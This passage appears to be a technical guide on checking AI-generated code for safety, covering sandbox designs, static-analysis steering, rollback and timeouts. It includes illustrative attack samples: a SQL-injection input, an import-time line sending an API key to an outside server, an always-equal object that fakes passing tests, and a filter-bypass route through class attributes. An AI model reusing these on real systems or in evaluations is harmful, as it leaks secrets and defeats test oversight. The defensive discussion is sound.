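Finished code is unsafe if it violates the policy in at least one of the conditions in which it might run. A condition includes the code's inputs, the files around it, the time and any random choices. One run that violates the policy in such a condition therefore proves that the code is unsafe. A clean run rules out a violation only in the condition tried, and only for as long as the run lasted.

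Repeated runs catch more faults but can still miss rare ones. If a fault appears in 1% of runs, there is about an 82% chance (0.99^20) that 20 independent runs will all be clean. This calculation assumes that the test conditions resemble real use, but an attacker can choose the condition that triggers the fault. Wu, Chen and colleagues note that a harmful program could also detect the sandbox, wait until later or spread its damage over several commands that each look harmless. Their benchmarks don't include such an attacker. Retrying makes the problem worse because each new attempt is another chance for a harmful step to run cleanly.

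An observed violation is much stronger evidence, but like an exception, it counts only if the finished code could run under the same conditions. Suppose an unfinished script deletes every file for which `is_temporary(path)` returns true, and a stand-in for that function always returns true. The run then deletes files that the real function would have protected, so the verdict should be "unknown".

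Vulnerable code can run cleanly for a different reason, which is that the harm requires an attacker's input:

```python
def find_user(db, name):
    query = "SELECT * FROM users WHERE name = '" + name + "'"
    return db.execute(query).fetchall()
```

The function returns Ana's record when given the name `Ana`, but it returns every user's record when given `' OR '1'='1`, because the quotation mark ends the name and the database treats the rest as part of the query. Both runs read the same database and make no connections, so both would pass a policy about files and connections. Catching the fault would require a policy that limits which records a caller may receive and a test that includes a malicious name.

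A system can at least avoid overstating what it has checked. *MuninAI* (2026) describes an assistant for research groups that labels all generated code as executed, compiled or only checked for style. A similar label for safety could read "no violations on two inputs in ten seconds" instead of "safe".

### Matching the test to the harm

An output can be dangerous in three ways, and a sandboxed run is a good test for only one of them:

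| Harm | Example | Suitable test | What a clean run shows |
|---|---|---|---|
| The code does damage when it runs. | a loop that deletes the wrong folder | an effect policy and a sandboxed run | no damage in the conditions tried |
| Someone can exploit the code later. | `find_user` | security analysis or simulated attacks | little, unless the run includes an attack |
| The text is harmful to read. | instructions for making a poison | a trained classifier or a judge model | nothing |

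*PurpCode* (2025), which describes how to train a safer coding model, separates the tests in a similar way. It uses a code analyser to find vulnerabilities, a language model to judge whether a response helps with an attack, and test runs to check whether the code is useful.

Some outputs belong in more than one row. A program that encrypts someone's files for ransom does damage when it runs, and giving it to a criminal is also harmful. A sandboxed run might show only that the program encrypts a folder, which a backup program could also do. The difference is who asked for the program and why, so the system also has to evaluate the request.

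### Replacing a predicted outcome with an executed one

An agent can also predict what an action will do instead of trying it on a copy. Zhao, Liu and colleagues (2026) tested both approaches in *Predictive Safety Guardrails Do Not Always Make LLM Agents Safer*. In their main setup, a language model predicts the consequences of each action before the agent takes it. If the predicted risk is too high, the system blocks the action and the agent proposes another, which the system also checks. In a variation, the system runs the action in a separate copy of the current state and checks the actual outcome against the available safety rules.

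They compared the two on HarnessAudit, a set of digital office tasks with limits on which tools, files and information an agent may use. Each cell in the table shows two scores from 0 to 100, the first for respecting those limits and the second for completing the task.

| Agent | No check | Predicted outcome | Executed outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.5-27B | 76.8 / 83.6 | 85.1 / 82.4 | 84.7 / 78.3 |
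| GLM-5.3-Flash | 64.4 / 85.7 | 74.5 / 77.3 | 73.8 / 78.6 |
| Gemini-3.7-Flash | 69.5 / 88.1 | 72.2 / 88.2 | 82.4 / 89.7 |

Both kinds of check improved safety for all three agents. Only Gemini did clearly better when the check executed the action instead of predicting its outcome, with its safety score rising by another ten points. For the other two, safety hardly changed, and Qwen completed less of its work. Small differences here probably mean little, because Qwen's safety score without any check varied between 76.8 and 78.8 across three sets of runs.

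Zhao and colleagues call the executed result "correct feedback", but only for one action, in the restored state, under the available safety checks. This feedback doesn't establish that the rest of the task will be safe, and violations did occur later. The researchers conclude that agents don't use reliable information faithfully in later decisions. That is plausible, but the violations might also have come from rules that the sandbox didn't check or actions that the system didn't test.

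Their other evidence for this conclusion is weaker than it looks. When they replaced the explanations in the predictions with irrelevant text, Qwen's safety score rose by 3.5 points, but they left the judgement of risk in place, so the system could still block dangerous actions. The result shows that blocking can work without a useful explanation, but not that the predictions made no difference. When they reversed the judgements as well, Gemini's safety score reached 100 while its completion score fell to 4.7. An agent that does almost nothing breaks few rules, so a safety score means little without a measure of completed work.

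This study checks complete actions, such as filing a report, and Caper checks complete shell commands. No published study appears to have tested whether running partial programs during generation catches harmful code. The studies that run unfinished code measured whether the finished program worked, and Sun and colleagues also measured how much time early execution saves. *Do Uncertainty Signals Help?* by Wu and colleagues comes closest. It tried rollback on security patches from Dsec-Python, but scored how well the patches matched the intended edit, not what they did when they ran. The deleted-folder example therefore shows how such a check could work, but how often it would miss harmful code or reject safe code is unknown.

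### Security analysis while the model writes

A builder can use a static check to search code for known weaknesses that someone could exploit later. Such weaknesses are common even in code from capable agents. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026), a survey, cites a test of 105 C and C++ tasks in which the best pairing of agent and model produced correct and secure code only 23.8% of the time.

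Static analysers are good at finding dangerous code that is present, such as a database query built by joining strings. According to *SPLASH* (2026), they often miss flaws that consist of an absent check, because there is no pattern to match. Unfinished programs add another difficulty because, as *LLMs + Security = Trouble* (2026) points out, code that hasn't yet cleaned a user's input may still do so later. *Constrained Code Generation with Diffusion Language Models* (2026) describes one way to handle this, a detector that searches partial programs for a path from untrusted input to a dangerous operation with no cleaning step in between. In `find_user`, the verdict would be unknown after the first line. Once the model has written the call to `db.execute`, cleaning the name on a later line would be too late. The function could still be safe if every caller cleans the name first, so even this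 verdict depends on code outside the function.

In *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation*, Lunghi, Djire and colleagues (2026) tested analyzing code while a model generates it. Their software runs Semgrep, which compares code with patterns of known weaknesses, after every line that leaves the program syntactically valid. When Semgrep raises an alert, a method they call Steering removes the flagged line and everything after it, adds the warning and a recommended fix to the prompt, and lets the model continue.

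The experiments used three sets of Python tasks. RiskyPy contains tasks chosen because analysers raise alerts on their solutions, SecEvalPlus contains many weaknesses that analysers can't detect, and BaxBench consists of web applications that the experimenters attack. The table gives the share of programs that worked and were secure, first without guidance and then with Steering.

| Model | RiskyPy | SecEvalPlus | BaxBench |
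|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-Coder-14B | 31.5% → 28.8% | 9.3% → 6.4% | 4.8% → 3.6% |
| Qwen2.5-72B | 34.7% → 30.6% | 12.9% → 14.0% | 10.3% → 10.3% |
| DeepSeek-V4.1-flash | 52.5% → 64.4% | 31.4% → 34.8% | 38.9% → 28.6% |

Of these changes, only DeepSeek's gain on RiskyPy and its loss on BaxBench were statistically significant. The gain is also not entirely due to the analyser. DeepSeek reached 63.5% on RiskyPy just by criticising and revising its own finished programs, although this took about 18 times as many output tokens as unguided generation, compared with 1.7 times as many for steering. Steering took almost ten times as long as unguided generation, because the software had to run the analyser after each line and restart the model after each alert.

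Missed vulnerabilities limited what Steering could achieve. On SecEvalPlus, between 62% and 87% of the working programs were insecure, but Semgrep and a second analyser, Bandit, flagged at most 5.6% of those insecure programs. On RiskyPy, they flagged most of the insecure programs, but between 39% and 52% of the working programs they flagged had no exploitable weakness, according to a language model that judged their security. The model's judgements are uncertain, since two human experts who labelled 50 programs agreed with each other on only 66% of them. The model agreed with each expert slightly more often than that.

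Programmers tend to ignore false alarms, so false alarms do more damage when a model receives them. The applications in BaxBench have to accept connections from outside their container, but one Semgrep rule warns against the setting that allows this. Steering told the models to put the task first if a recommendation conflicted with it. The models still removed the setting in 79 of 83 cases where the program had worked before. Successful attacks on DeepSeek's applications fell from 32.1% to 22.2%, partly because attackers can't reach an application that accepts no outside connections.

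The kind of fix also mattered. Replacing an unsafe XML parser with a safe one is a local change, and Steering did more good than harm with that rule for two of the three models. Removing `eval`, which runs text as code, often means restructuring the program. DeepSeek managed this in 21 of 33 cases without breaking a program, while the larger Qwen model succeeded in two of 63 and broke 23 programs. Lunghi and colleagues therefore recommend filtering alerts before they reach the model, keeping only those that have a clear, local fix and don't conflict with the task.

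A builder shouldn't measure success with the same analyser that guided the model. On RiskyPy, Steering raised the share of DeepSeek's programs that worked and triggered no alerts from 10.0% to 57.1%, a gain of 47 percentage points. The share that worked and were secure rose by only 12 points. Some of the difference comes from false alarms that disappeared, but some programs lost their alerts and still had a weakness. A separate security test on the finished program can still catch these weaknesses.

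## Isolating the code that is being checked

A check that runs code has to do so before anyone knows whether the code is safe. During generation, the system may run such a check after every line. Even without these checks, a single agent task can run dozens of short commands a minute, as Wang and Zheng (2026) point out in *Sandlock*.

Code can also run when the builder only meant to load it. Suppose a model is writing a file called `report.py`, and the checker wants to test the function `total`:

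```python
import os, urllib.request

key = os.environ.get("API_KEY", "")
urllib.request.urlopen("http://example.com/?k=" + key)

def total(rows):
    return sum(row["price"] for row in rows)
```

The checker has to import the file before it can call `total`. Python runs every top-level statement during an import, so the code sends the key to a stranger's server before the test begins. The sandbox therefore has to be active before the import.

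### What needs protection

| At risk | Example |
|---|---|
| The host | The code deletes files outside its folder. |
| Credentials | The code reads a private key or a password. |
| The network | The code attacks another machine or sends data out. |
| Other users' runs | The code reads another user's files in a shared folder. |
| The tests and the verdict | The code makes a failing test appear to pass. |

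The last risk is easy to overlook. One of Schneider's conditions for enforcement was that a program must not be able to alter its monitor, and a test that runs in the same process as the code breaks this condition. Suppose the test is `merge_logs(a, b) == expected`, and the model writes:

```python
class Match:
    def __eq__(self, other):
        return True

def merge_logs(a, b):
    return Match()
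```

Python lets an object define what counts as equal to it, so a function can pass every equality test by returning an object that equals everything. To prevent this, the builder can send only the inputs into the sandbox, accept only plain data such as JSON in return, and compare that data with the expected output outside the sandbox. The word "passed" in the printed output shouldn't count as a verdict, because the code being checked can print it too.

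The barrier's required strength depends on who might have influenced the code. In *SPEAR*, Lu, Feng and colleagues (2026) describe a LinkedIn agent that writes Python to analyse internal data, and they assume that the model and the data are trustworthy. Wang and Zheng assume that an attacker may have shaped the code or the data it reads. Their assumption is safer for any assistant that reads web pages or downloaded files, because instructions hidden in that text can change what the model writes, even if the user is honest.

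### Filters on the source code

The lightest barrier is a check of the code before it runs. Software parses the code into a syntax tree, which has a node for each construct, such as a loop or an import, and rejects the code if the tree contains a forbidden node. The software may also remove built-in functions such as `open` and `eval`. The code then runs in an ordinary Python interpreter. This adds almost no start-up time or memory, but the code has the same access to the host as the process that runs it.

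A strict filter can cause little disruption if the task is narrow. *DrugClaw and DrugAudit* (2026) describes an agent that answers questions about medicines and is not allowed to write `while` loops, `with` blocks or classes. The filter rejects fewer than 1% of the agent's programs. A general coding assistant could hardly work under these rules, because ordinary programs need classes. *STELP* (2026) uses a list of permitted constructs, built-in functions and library modules, and allows `while` loops except `while True`.

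Filters can also block useful work. Deekshith, Prabha and colleagues (2026) tested *ExecuGraph*, a system of six model agents, on 30 textbook programming problems. About 23% of the full system's trials failed, and 41% of those failures were sandbox violations, a larger share than wrong answers. The sandbox therefore stopped almost one trial in ten. Textbook problems rarely require a program to touch files or other processes, so some of the blocked code was probably harmless.

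A filter for Python code has difficulty meeting Schneider's condition that a monitor must recognise every way of performing a forbidden act. Every Python object has a link to its class, and a program can follow such links to reach much of what the interpreter has loaded. Deleting the name `open` therefore doesn't delete the function. A filter can reject suspicious attribute names, but `"{0.__class__}".format(x)` reads an attribute whose name is inside a string, which the syntax tree represents only as text. Permitted libraries add further routes, such as the functions for reading and writing files in the data library pandas.

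Several developers acknowledge that their filters wouldn't stop a determined attacker. Lu and colleagues call filters like theirs "known-leaky" and recommend a container or WebAssembly for untrusted content. They recorded no escape attempts in more than 200 runs, but describe this as operational experience, not a security evaluation. *EffGen* (2026), which describes an agent framework for small models, recommends running its filtered Python session inside a Docker container in production. Deekshith and colleagues run the code in a new process without the parent's environment variables, which keeps an access token out of reach, but also advise stronger isolation if the code may be hostile.

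*A hardware-safety-gated system for LLM-written native ARTIQ control code* (2026) reports testing a filter with 1,932 adversarial scripts for controlling a quantum physics experiment. Some of the scripts that the filter approved fell outside its protection, either by design or because of gaps that remain open. For example, the filter checks only the devices that the operator has declared. In addition, a separate tool for examining a submitted file runs the file, much as an import does, without sending it through the filter.

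A filter is still useful as a quick first check, since it can reject code before it runs and explain why. Cho, Hachiuma and colleagues (2026) use one this way in *SpatialClaw*, an agent that analyses images with Python. If the filter rejects a piece of code, the model receives a short error message and rewrites the code.

### Restricted system calls

To open a file or a network connection, a program has to make a system call, which is a request to the operating system's kernel. Linux can restrict which system calls a process may make and which files it may access. A disguised call to `open` then fails just like an ordinary one, so the builder doesn't have to anticipate how the source code might hide it.

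Wang and Zheng's Sandlock divides this work between the kernel and a supervisor, a process outside the sandbox. The kernel enforces fixed rules, such as which folders the code may read. The supervisor makes decisions that depend on values known only at run time, such as the address of a connection.

Checking such values creates a race condition. The program could request a permitted address, wait for the supervisor to approve it, then replace it in memory before the kernel reads it. Sandlock prevents this by copying the address once, checking the copy and using that copy to open the connection on the program's behalf.

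A trivial command took about 6 milliseconds to run in Sandlock, 5 more than without it. Docker took roughly 44 times as long as Sandlock. Python, Node and the test tool pytest ran unmodified once they had access to their temporary folders. Wang and Zheng also ran ten tests of what the policy should allow or deny, and all ten passed. These tests covered expected behaviour and did not include a serious attempt to break out of Sandlock.

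The code still uses the host's kernel, so a kernel error could let the code escape. Sandlock's memory limit also relies on the supervisor counting requests, which suits buggy programs better than hostile ones. For hostile users who share a machine, Wang and Zheng recommend a virtual machine.

### Containers, user-space kernels and microVMs

A container gives a group of processes its own view of files, processes and the network, but the host's kernel still handles their system calls. Memory is rarely a problem. *Computer Environments Elicit General Agentic Intelligence in LLMs* (2026) reports about 50 MB for an idle container and 200 MB at peak, so 512 containers needed about 100 GB, or 5% of a large server's memory. The containers shared one 1.1 GB image.

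gVisor places a second kernel, written as an ordinary program, between the code and the host. It answers most system calls itself and makes only a limited set of calls to the host. This reduces the code's contact with the host's kernel, but system calls take longer, and some build tools depend on details that gVisor doesn't reproduce.

A microVM is a small virtual machine with its own kernel. The processor's virtualisation features separate it from the host, and a program such as Firecracker supplies its virtual disk and network card. To reach the host, an attacker would usually have to take over the microVM's kernel and then exploit an error in Firecracker or in the host's virtualisation code.

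In *AI Code Sandboxes*, Andronchik and Lokhmakov (2026) compared five products, each with its default settings, on one Linux server. They counted how many of 28 probes revealed details of the host, and how many of 14 kernel features used in known attacks were reachable from inside the sandbox.

| Product | Barrier | Kinds of host call permitted | Host details revealed | Attack features reachable |
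|---|---|---|---|---|
| Daytona | container | no filter | 10 of 28 | 11 of 14 |
| gVisor | user-space kernel | 84 | 2 of 28 | 5 of 14 |
| e2b | Firecracker microVM | 55 | 0 of 28 | 7 of 14 |
| microsandbox | libkrun microVM | no filter | 0 of 28 | 11 of 14 |
| arrakis | Cloud Hypervisor microVM | filter on 32 of 33 threads | 1 of 28 | 12 of 14 |

The last column doesn't rank the products by safety, because a reachable feature isn't necessarily exploitable. The effect of an attack would also depend on the product. In a microVM it would normally hit the guest's kernel first, while in Daytona it would hit the host's kernel directly. Daytona also revealed the serial numbers of the host's disks, which would let code recognise the machine later.

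A sandbox's settings can matter as much as the type of barrier it uses. Daytona starts its containers in privileged mode, which turns off Docker's standard system-call filter, and the operator can't turn the filter back on without changing Daytona's source code. In arrakis, ordinary code inside the guest could open the device used to create further virtual machines, which exposes a large and complicated part of the kernel.

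A lack of known vulnerabilities isn't strong evidence of safety. libkrun has none published, but its developers don't test it with automatically generated inputs, and Andronchik and Lokhmakov found no academic study of it, so they left it out of their ranking by past vulnerabilities.

### WebAssembly

WebAssembly is an instruction set for programs that run inside an engine, such as the one in a web browser. The program can use only its own block of memory and the functions the engine provides. If the engine provides no function for opening files, the program cannot open them. *A Survey of Vibe Coding with Large Language Models* (2025) describes such engines as deterministic and memory-safe environments for untrusted code.

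The WebAssembly engine usually runs as an ordinary process on the host, so an error in it, or a function that grants too much access, could let the code reach the host. A builder can run the engine inside a restricted process to limit the damage. Python needs an interpreter compiled for WebAssembly, and libraries that contain machine code need special versions. WebAssembly is therefore easier to use for small functions than for projects with many dependencies.

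The table compares the barriers. All the start-up times come from Wang and Zheng, but they timed only Sandlock and Docker in their experiments, so the other times are rough guides.

| Barrier | What the code shares with the host | Start-up | Main remaining weakness |
|---|---|---|---|
| Source filter | the interpreter, often with the checker | almost none | a route that the filter doesn't cover |
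| Restricted process (Sandlock) | the kernel | 6 ms | an error in the kernel |
| Container (Docker without root) | the kernel | 300 ms | an error in the kernel, or excessive privileges |
| gVisor | a small part of the kernel's interface | 200 ms | an error in gVisor |
| MicroVM (Firecracker) | the processor and virtual devices | 100 ms | an error in the virtualisation software |
| WebAssembly | the engine's process | depends on the engine | an error in the engine, or a function that allows too much |

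Coding agents differ widely in how they isolate the code they run. According to *Harness Engineering* (2026), a study of the source code of eleven agents, OpenAI's Codex had the most thorough sandbox in July 2026. Anthropic's Claude Code had a sandbox, but users had to turn it on. OpenCode relied only on policy rules. A builder who adds checks to an existing agent therefore can't assume that the agent isolates the code it runs.

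### Keeping state between checks

The simplest approach is to run each check in a new sandbox, so nothing from a rejected attempt can affect the next one. For 50 checks, start-up alone would take about 15 seconds with rootless Docker, 5 seconds with Firecracker and 0.3 seconds with Sandlock.

Repeating earlier work can slow down checking considerably. Suppose a script has 50 statements that take 0.1 seconds each. Running it once takes 5 seconds. If the system checks after every statement and starts from the beginning each time, it executes 1 + 2 + … + 50 = 1,275 statements, which takes 127.5 seconds.

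A persistent session avoids the repetition. SpatialClaw keeps variables available from one piece of code to the next and discards the session only when the task ends. But a statement may change the session before the system rejects it. If the model writes `last = rows.pop()` and the system rejects the line after running it, `rows` has already lost its last entry, and running a corrected version in the same session removes another.

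Forking lets the system undo a statement's changes to memory. The process makes a copy of itself, and the copy runs the new statement. If the statement passes, the system continues with the copy. Otherwise, it deletes the copy and returns to the original. The two share memory until one changes it, so copying is fast. On an ordinary workstation, Sandlock created 1,000 such copies in about 530 milliseconds.

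A fork doesn't copy files, and the two processes share their position in any file that was already open. If the trial run reads from that file, the original process continues from the wrong place. Sandlock has a separate copy-on-write layer for files, which redirects all changes to another folder so that the system can keep or discard them together. The loop that deleted `/work/build_scripts` could run on this layer and leave the real folder untouched. However, Sandlock doesn't yet give each forked process its own layer, so a builder has to coordinate forking with the file layer.

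A snapshot of a virtual machine can save memory, files and running processes together. Including memory makes the snapshot larger. E2b's default guest has about half a gigabyte of memory, and arrakis's has about 19 gigabytes. Storing only what has changed since the previous snapshot reduces the amount of data to save. Machines restored from the same snapshot also start with their random number generators in the same state, so two attempts may produce identical "random" values unless the software resets the generators.

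### Requests that have left the sandbox

Restoring a snapshot cannot undo an effect outside the sandbox, such as a sent email, a payment or an uploaded password. The restored sandbox also contains no record of the effect, so the next attempt may send the email or make the payment again.

The default should therefore be no network access, which *MuninAI* describes as standard practice. This can hurt performance on tasks that need current information. Changing only the network setting shifted MuninAI's accuracy on the same set of literature questions by 17 to 21 percentage points. Code usually needs the network for a more limited purpose, such as installing libraries. The system can install them in advance and cut the connection before it runs anything the model wrote.

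If the code calls an outside service, a simulated version inside the sandbox can return prepared answers. Wang and Zheng instead suggest holding outgoing web requests until the system accepts the step. That would work for a notification, but not for a request whose answer the next line of code uses.

Permitting only certain servers may not stop a program from sending out stolen data, because an attacker may have an account on a permitted service and receive the data there. A useful rule may therefore have to specify the exact page and type of request. A program can also leak data by hiding it in a server name that it looks up. Sandlock looks up permitted names once at the start and fixes their addresses for the rest of the run.

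Such boundaries have failed even at companies that specialise in AI. In July 2026, Anthropic disclosed that its models had breached three real organisations during misconfigured evaluations (*Anthropic says Claude models breached 3 organizations during cybersecurity tests*, Anadolu Agency, 2026). In September, OpenAI reported that an agent in a training run had got past its network filtering and contacted an outside chatbot (*OpenAI pauses training of top AI models after agent bypasses internet curbs*, Press Trust of India, 2026).

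### A default configuration and its tests

For a service that runs code for several users, a reasonable default is:

```text
Outer barrier:    one Firecracker microVM per task, deleted afterwards
Each check:       a new restricted process inside the microVM, without root
Files:            read-only system, copy-on-write work folder, nothing from the host
Credentials:      none in files or environment variables
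Network:          none; simulated services inside the microVM
Limits:           time, memory, number of processes
Tests:            inputs go in, JSON comes out, comparison happens outside
```

The microVM separates users from one another, and the restricted processes keep the overhead of each check low. If Sandlock ran as fast inside the microVM as it did on Wang and Zheng's workstation, 50 checks would add about 0.4 seconds of start-up time. But Sandlock requires Linux 6.12 or later, and e2b's guest used 6.1 when Andronchik and Lokhmakov tested it, so Sandlock would not run there. A builder could supply a newer guest kernel or use another tool for the inner process.

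gVisor is a good alternative on machines without hardware virtualisation. For a single developer whose model reads only trusted material, a restricted process may be enough.

Before using the sandbox, the builder should run small test programs inside it:

| Test program | Required result |
|---|---|
| Import a module whose first line writes outside the work folder. | The write fails. |
| Search files and environment variables for a fake key that the builder left on the host. | The key doesn't appear. |
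| Contact the builder's own outside server by name and by address. | The server and the name-lookup log show no contact. |
| Call a simulated service. | The service answers. |
| Write a file in the work folder, then restore the earlier state. | The write works, and the file then disappears. |
| Open the folder of another run. | The attempt fails. |
| Return a `Match` object, or print "passed" and exit. | The verdict is fail. |
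| Open `/dev/kvm`, the device for creating virtual machines. | The attempt fails. |

Some of these tests require an operation to succeed, because a sandbox in which nothing works would otherwise pass. For the network test, the builder should rely on the outside server's records, because an error inside the sandbox may mean only that the reply was blocked after the request had gone out.

The tests can also be wrong. In early runs, Andronchik and Lokhmakov examined only the main thread of arrakis's virtual machine software and missed the system-call filter on the other 32 threads. They also recorded "inconclusive" separately from "pass" and "fail", which is sensible here too, since a test program that crashes before it attempts the forbidden operation doesn't show whether that operation would be blocked.

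The builder should repeat the tests after every change to the configuration. The builder should also check the age of the software, because a sandbox can pass every test in the table and still lack recent security fixes. When Andronchik and Lokhmakov examined e2b, its default self-hosting setup used a version of Firecracker that the developers had chosen 399 days earlier.

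## Setting time limits and deciding how often to check

Even in a well-isolated sandbox, a program can run forever. A checker that waits for such a program never returns a verdict, and the model can't continue. No general procedure can identify these programs in advance, a result that goes back to Alan Turing's work in 1936. To see why, suppose a function `halts` could always tell whether a program eventually stops:

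```python
def contrary():
    if halts(contrary):
        while True:
            pass
```

If `halts` returns true, `contrary` loops forever, and if `halts` returns false, `contrary` stops at once. The answer is wrong either way, so `halts` can't exist.

Many individual programs can still be proved to stop. *Verifier-Grounded Agentic RL for Provably Correct Code* (Ma, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) trains models to write programs together with such proofs. Its verifiers require a quantity that decreases at every step and can't decrease forever. In a finished version of `merge_logs`, each pass through the loop moves one log entry, so the number of entries left falls by one. But everyday code rarely comes with a proof, so most systems need a time limit.

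Reaching the time limit shows only that the code takes longer than the limit on that machine, so the verdict is unknown. Anything the system observed before the limit still counts. If the code deleted a protected file in the first second, the verdict is fail even if the run never ends. A timeout is also a failure when speed is part of the task, as in programming competitions.

### Responding to a timeout

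Many test systems treat a timeout as a failure. *Deep Reinforcement Learning* (2026) gives a teaching example in which a model receives a reward of 1 if its code passes the tests, and 0 if the code fails or the tests take more than three seconds. This rule is simple but can be very misleading. *Executable but Unfaithful* (2026) reports on coding agents that wrote and repaired tests under a time limit for the whole job. With 60 seconds, 10.5% of the Java tests and 5.5% of the Python tests ran properly. With 600 seconds, 92.4% and 91.4% did, so most of the failures under the short limit were due to lack of time.

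A system can reject the step, let it through, or postpone the decision by retrying with a longer limit or leaving it to a later check:

| Response | Correctness check on unreleased code | Safety check before an action |
|---|---|---|
| Reject | discards good code that happens to be slow | prevents harm, but also blocks slow harmless actions |
| Let through | acceptable if a later check covers the same code | unacceptable |
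| Retry or defer | usually the best choice | acceptable if the action waits for the verdict |

If a safety check counted a timeout as a pass, an attacker could easily evade it with harmful code that waits until the time limit has passed. A correctness test that times out in the middle of a file does little harm if the system tests the code again at the end. If that final test also times out, the system can reject the program or deliver it with a note that the test didn't finish. After a timeout, the message to the model should be "no result after five seconds" rather than "wrong answer", which could lead it to rewrite correct code.

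Some systems deliberately accept output when a checker is uncertain. *PYTHALAB-MERA* (Iscan, 2026) describes a controller for coding agents in which an optional judge model can veto a program only if it is highly confident. This is reasonable because the program has already passed the other checks, but it would be risky if the judge were the only safeguard. A lack of reported failures can also be misleading. Ma and colleagues score programs by how many required properties the verifier fails to prove, and a program that doesn't compile produces no such reports. They therefore had to give such programs a score of zero explicitly, or they would have received full marks for this part.

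If the time limit doubles with each retry, the failed attempts together never take more than twice as long as the run that finally succeeds. For example, suppose a check needs 7 seconds and the limits are 1, 2, 4 and 8 seconds. The three failed attempts take 7 seconds in total, and the successful one takes another 7.

A builder can also set two time limits for a check. The test runner nextest marks a test as slow after 60 seconds by default and has a separate option for stopping it, according to its *Slow tests and timeouts* documentation. Similarly, if a check takes longer than one second, a system could let the model continue writing while the check runs in the background, then stop the check after ten seconds.

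### Limiting more than time

Wall-clock time runs from the start of a program to its end, including any time it spends waiting. Processor time counts only the time during which processors work on the program. The difference can be large:

| Program | Wall-clock time | Processor time |
|---|---|---|
| waits 10 seconds for a reply | 10 s | almost none |
| calculates on an idle machine | 2 s | 2 s |
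| does the same calculation with a third of a processor | 6 s | 2 s |
| divides the calculation evenly among four processors | 0.5 s | 2 s |

On a busy machine, a limit on processor time is less likely than a wall-clock limit to stop correct code, but it would never stop a program that only waits. It makes sense to use processor time as the main limit and add a much higher wall-clock limit.

The time limit also has to stop the program. According to fast-check's *Time limits*, a timeout makes this test library ignore the result, but the code can keep running. On timeout, Python's `subprocess.run` kills the process it started, but not that process's children. The safest method is to put everything the check starts into one container or process group and stop the whole group. A limit on the number of processes keeps the code from creating them faster than the system can stop them.

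Memory needs its own limit because a program can use up a machine's memory long before its time runs out. Jha (2026), in *Does Fault Localization Beat a Fresh Attempt?*, reports that one generated program grew to 92 gigabytes. The system killed the process running it, which froze the pool of processes that ran all the other tests. Jha then gave each scoring job its own supervised process with a memory limit, so a runaway program could spoil only one task.

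A loop that prints forever can fill a disk, or the model's prompt if the system adds the output to it. Iscan limits the combined length of normal output and error messages. *EvilGenie* (2025), a benchmark that tests whether coding agents cheat, shortens the diagnostics for very large test cases. If a check must compare the full output with an expected result, a shortened output should count as unknown, like a timeout.

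### Choosing the limit

Jha originally allowed five seconds for every test. One correct solution needed about 5.1 seconds on his machine, so the same program passed or failed depending on what else the machine was doing. He replaced the fixed limit with a rule from EvalPlus, an extended set of tests for HumanEval and MBPP. EvalPlus' *Program Execution* gives the rule as

*T* = max(*T*_base, *k* × *T*_ref),

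where *T*_ref is the measured run time of a known correct solution, *T*_base is 1 second by default and *k* is 4. If the correct solution takes 0.1 seconds, the limit is 1 second, and if it takes 2 seconds, the limit is 8. EvalPlus recommends raising both settings on slow machines with erratic results.

The builder can set the limit by timing the same checks on existing code known to be good, since there is usually no correct solution to measure while a model is writing new code. The checks can be run many times on the machine that will do the work, under its usual load, and the limit should lie well above the slowest run. Rare timeouts add up over many checks, as a guard's false alarms do. If 1% of good checks exceed the limit, 33% of good programs would hit it at least once in 40 independent checks. At 0.1%, about 4% would. Slow runs tend to come in bursts when the machine is busy, so fewer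 programs would be affected overall, but many of them at once.

Published time limits differ mainly because they cover different amounts of work. The longest in the table below comes from *MathlibPR* (2026), a benchmark about proposed changes to a library of formal mathematics.

| Source | Limit | What has to finish in that time |
|---|---|---|
| EvalPlus | at least 1 s, 4 GB of memory | tests of a short function |
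| *Deep Reinforcement Learning* | 3 s | all unit tests for one answer |
| Deekshith and colleagues | 5 s by default | a function from a textbook problem, with its tests |
| *EvilGenie* | 6 s | one test case |
| Lu and colleagues | 60 s, 512 MB of memory | analysis of a data table by a trusted agent |
| *MathlibPR* | 180 to 900 s | a complete attempt by a model or agent |

OpenAI's agent Codex had a time limit of 900 seconds, but none of its completed attempts took more than 300. Recording run times shows whether a limit is longer than necessary.

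### How often to check

Suppose a model writes 50 tokens per second and a line of code has 12 tokens. Each line takes 0.24 seconds, so a 40-line program takes 9.6 seconds. If the model stops after every line for a 0.3-second check, about as long as a rootless Docker container takes to start, the checks add 12 seconds and more than double the total time. Checking every five lines adds only 2.4 seconds. The system then finds an error two lines later on average, because the error is equally likely to be anywhere from zero to four lines before the next check.

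A single timeout can take as long as many ordinary checks. If 2% of the 40 checks per program reach a five-second limit, each program has 0.8 timeouts on average, which add about 4 seconds.

The best interval depends on how often the model makes mistakes. Let *n* be the number of lines, *c* the time per check, *g* the time to write a line and *m* the average number of errors per program. With a check every *k* lines, checking takes *nc*/*k* seconds. The model also wastes about *mg*(*k* − 1)/2 seconds writing lines after an error that the system then discards. The sum is smallest when

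*k* = √(2*nc* / *mg*).

For one error per program, this gives *k* = 10:

| Lines between checks | Time for checks | Time wasted after the error | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 12.0 s | 0 s | 12.0 s |
| 5 | 2.4 s | 0.5 s | 2.9 s |
| 10 | 1.2 s | 1.1 s | 2.3 s |
| 20 | 0.6 s | 2.3 s | 2.9 s |
| 40 | 0.3 s | 4.7 s | 5.0 s |

With four errors per program, the best interval would be five lines. The calculation is only a rough guide, because it assumes that the system goes back exactly to the faulty line and leaves out the time for checking the rewritten lines. It also doesn't account for the possibility that an early report makes the error easier to repair, as Sun and colleagues found for data analysis scripts. Still, the totals for 5, 10 and 20 lines are close together, so a builder doesn't need to find the exact optimum.

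Different checks can also run at different intervals. Iscan's controller checks syntax, then looks for undefined names, then runs the program and tests its behaviour, stopping at the first failure. During generation, a system could check syntax after every line and run the tests only when a function is complete.

### Avoiding repeated work

These figures hold only when every check takes the same time, which isn't true if each check reruns the whole prefix. For 40 lines without loops, checking after every line would then execute 820 lines, compared with 40 in a session that keeps its variables. Even without such a session, checking every five lines would reduce the total to 180. Keeping the session adds little time. In Sun and colleagues' system, each call to a persistent Python session took about one millisecond, not counting the time to run the code itself.

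The system can also store verdicts and reuse them when the model writes the same code again. Jha asked models to replace only the lines that a failed test pointed to, and 48.9% of the attempts reproduced the old lines exactly. Others repeated earlier attempts, so only 23% of the resulting programs were distinct, and stored verdicts could have replaced roughly three quarters of the test runs. When the models wrote complete new solutions, 83% were distinct, which left much less to reuse.

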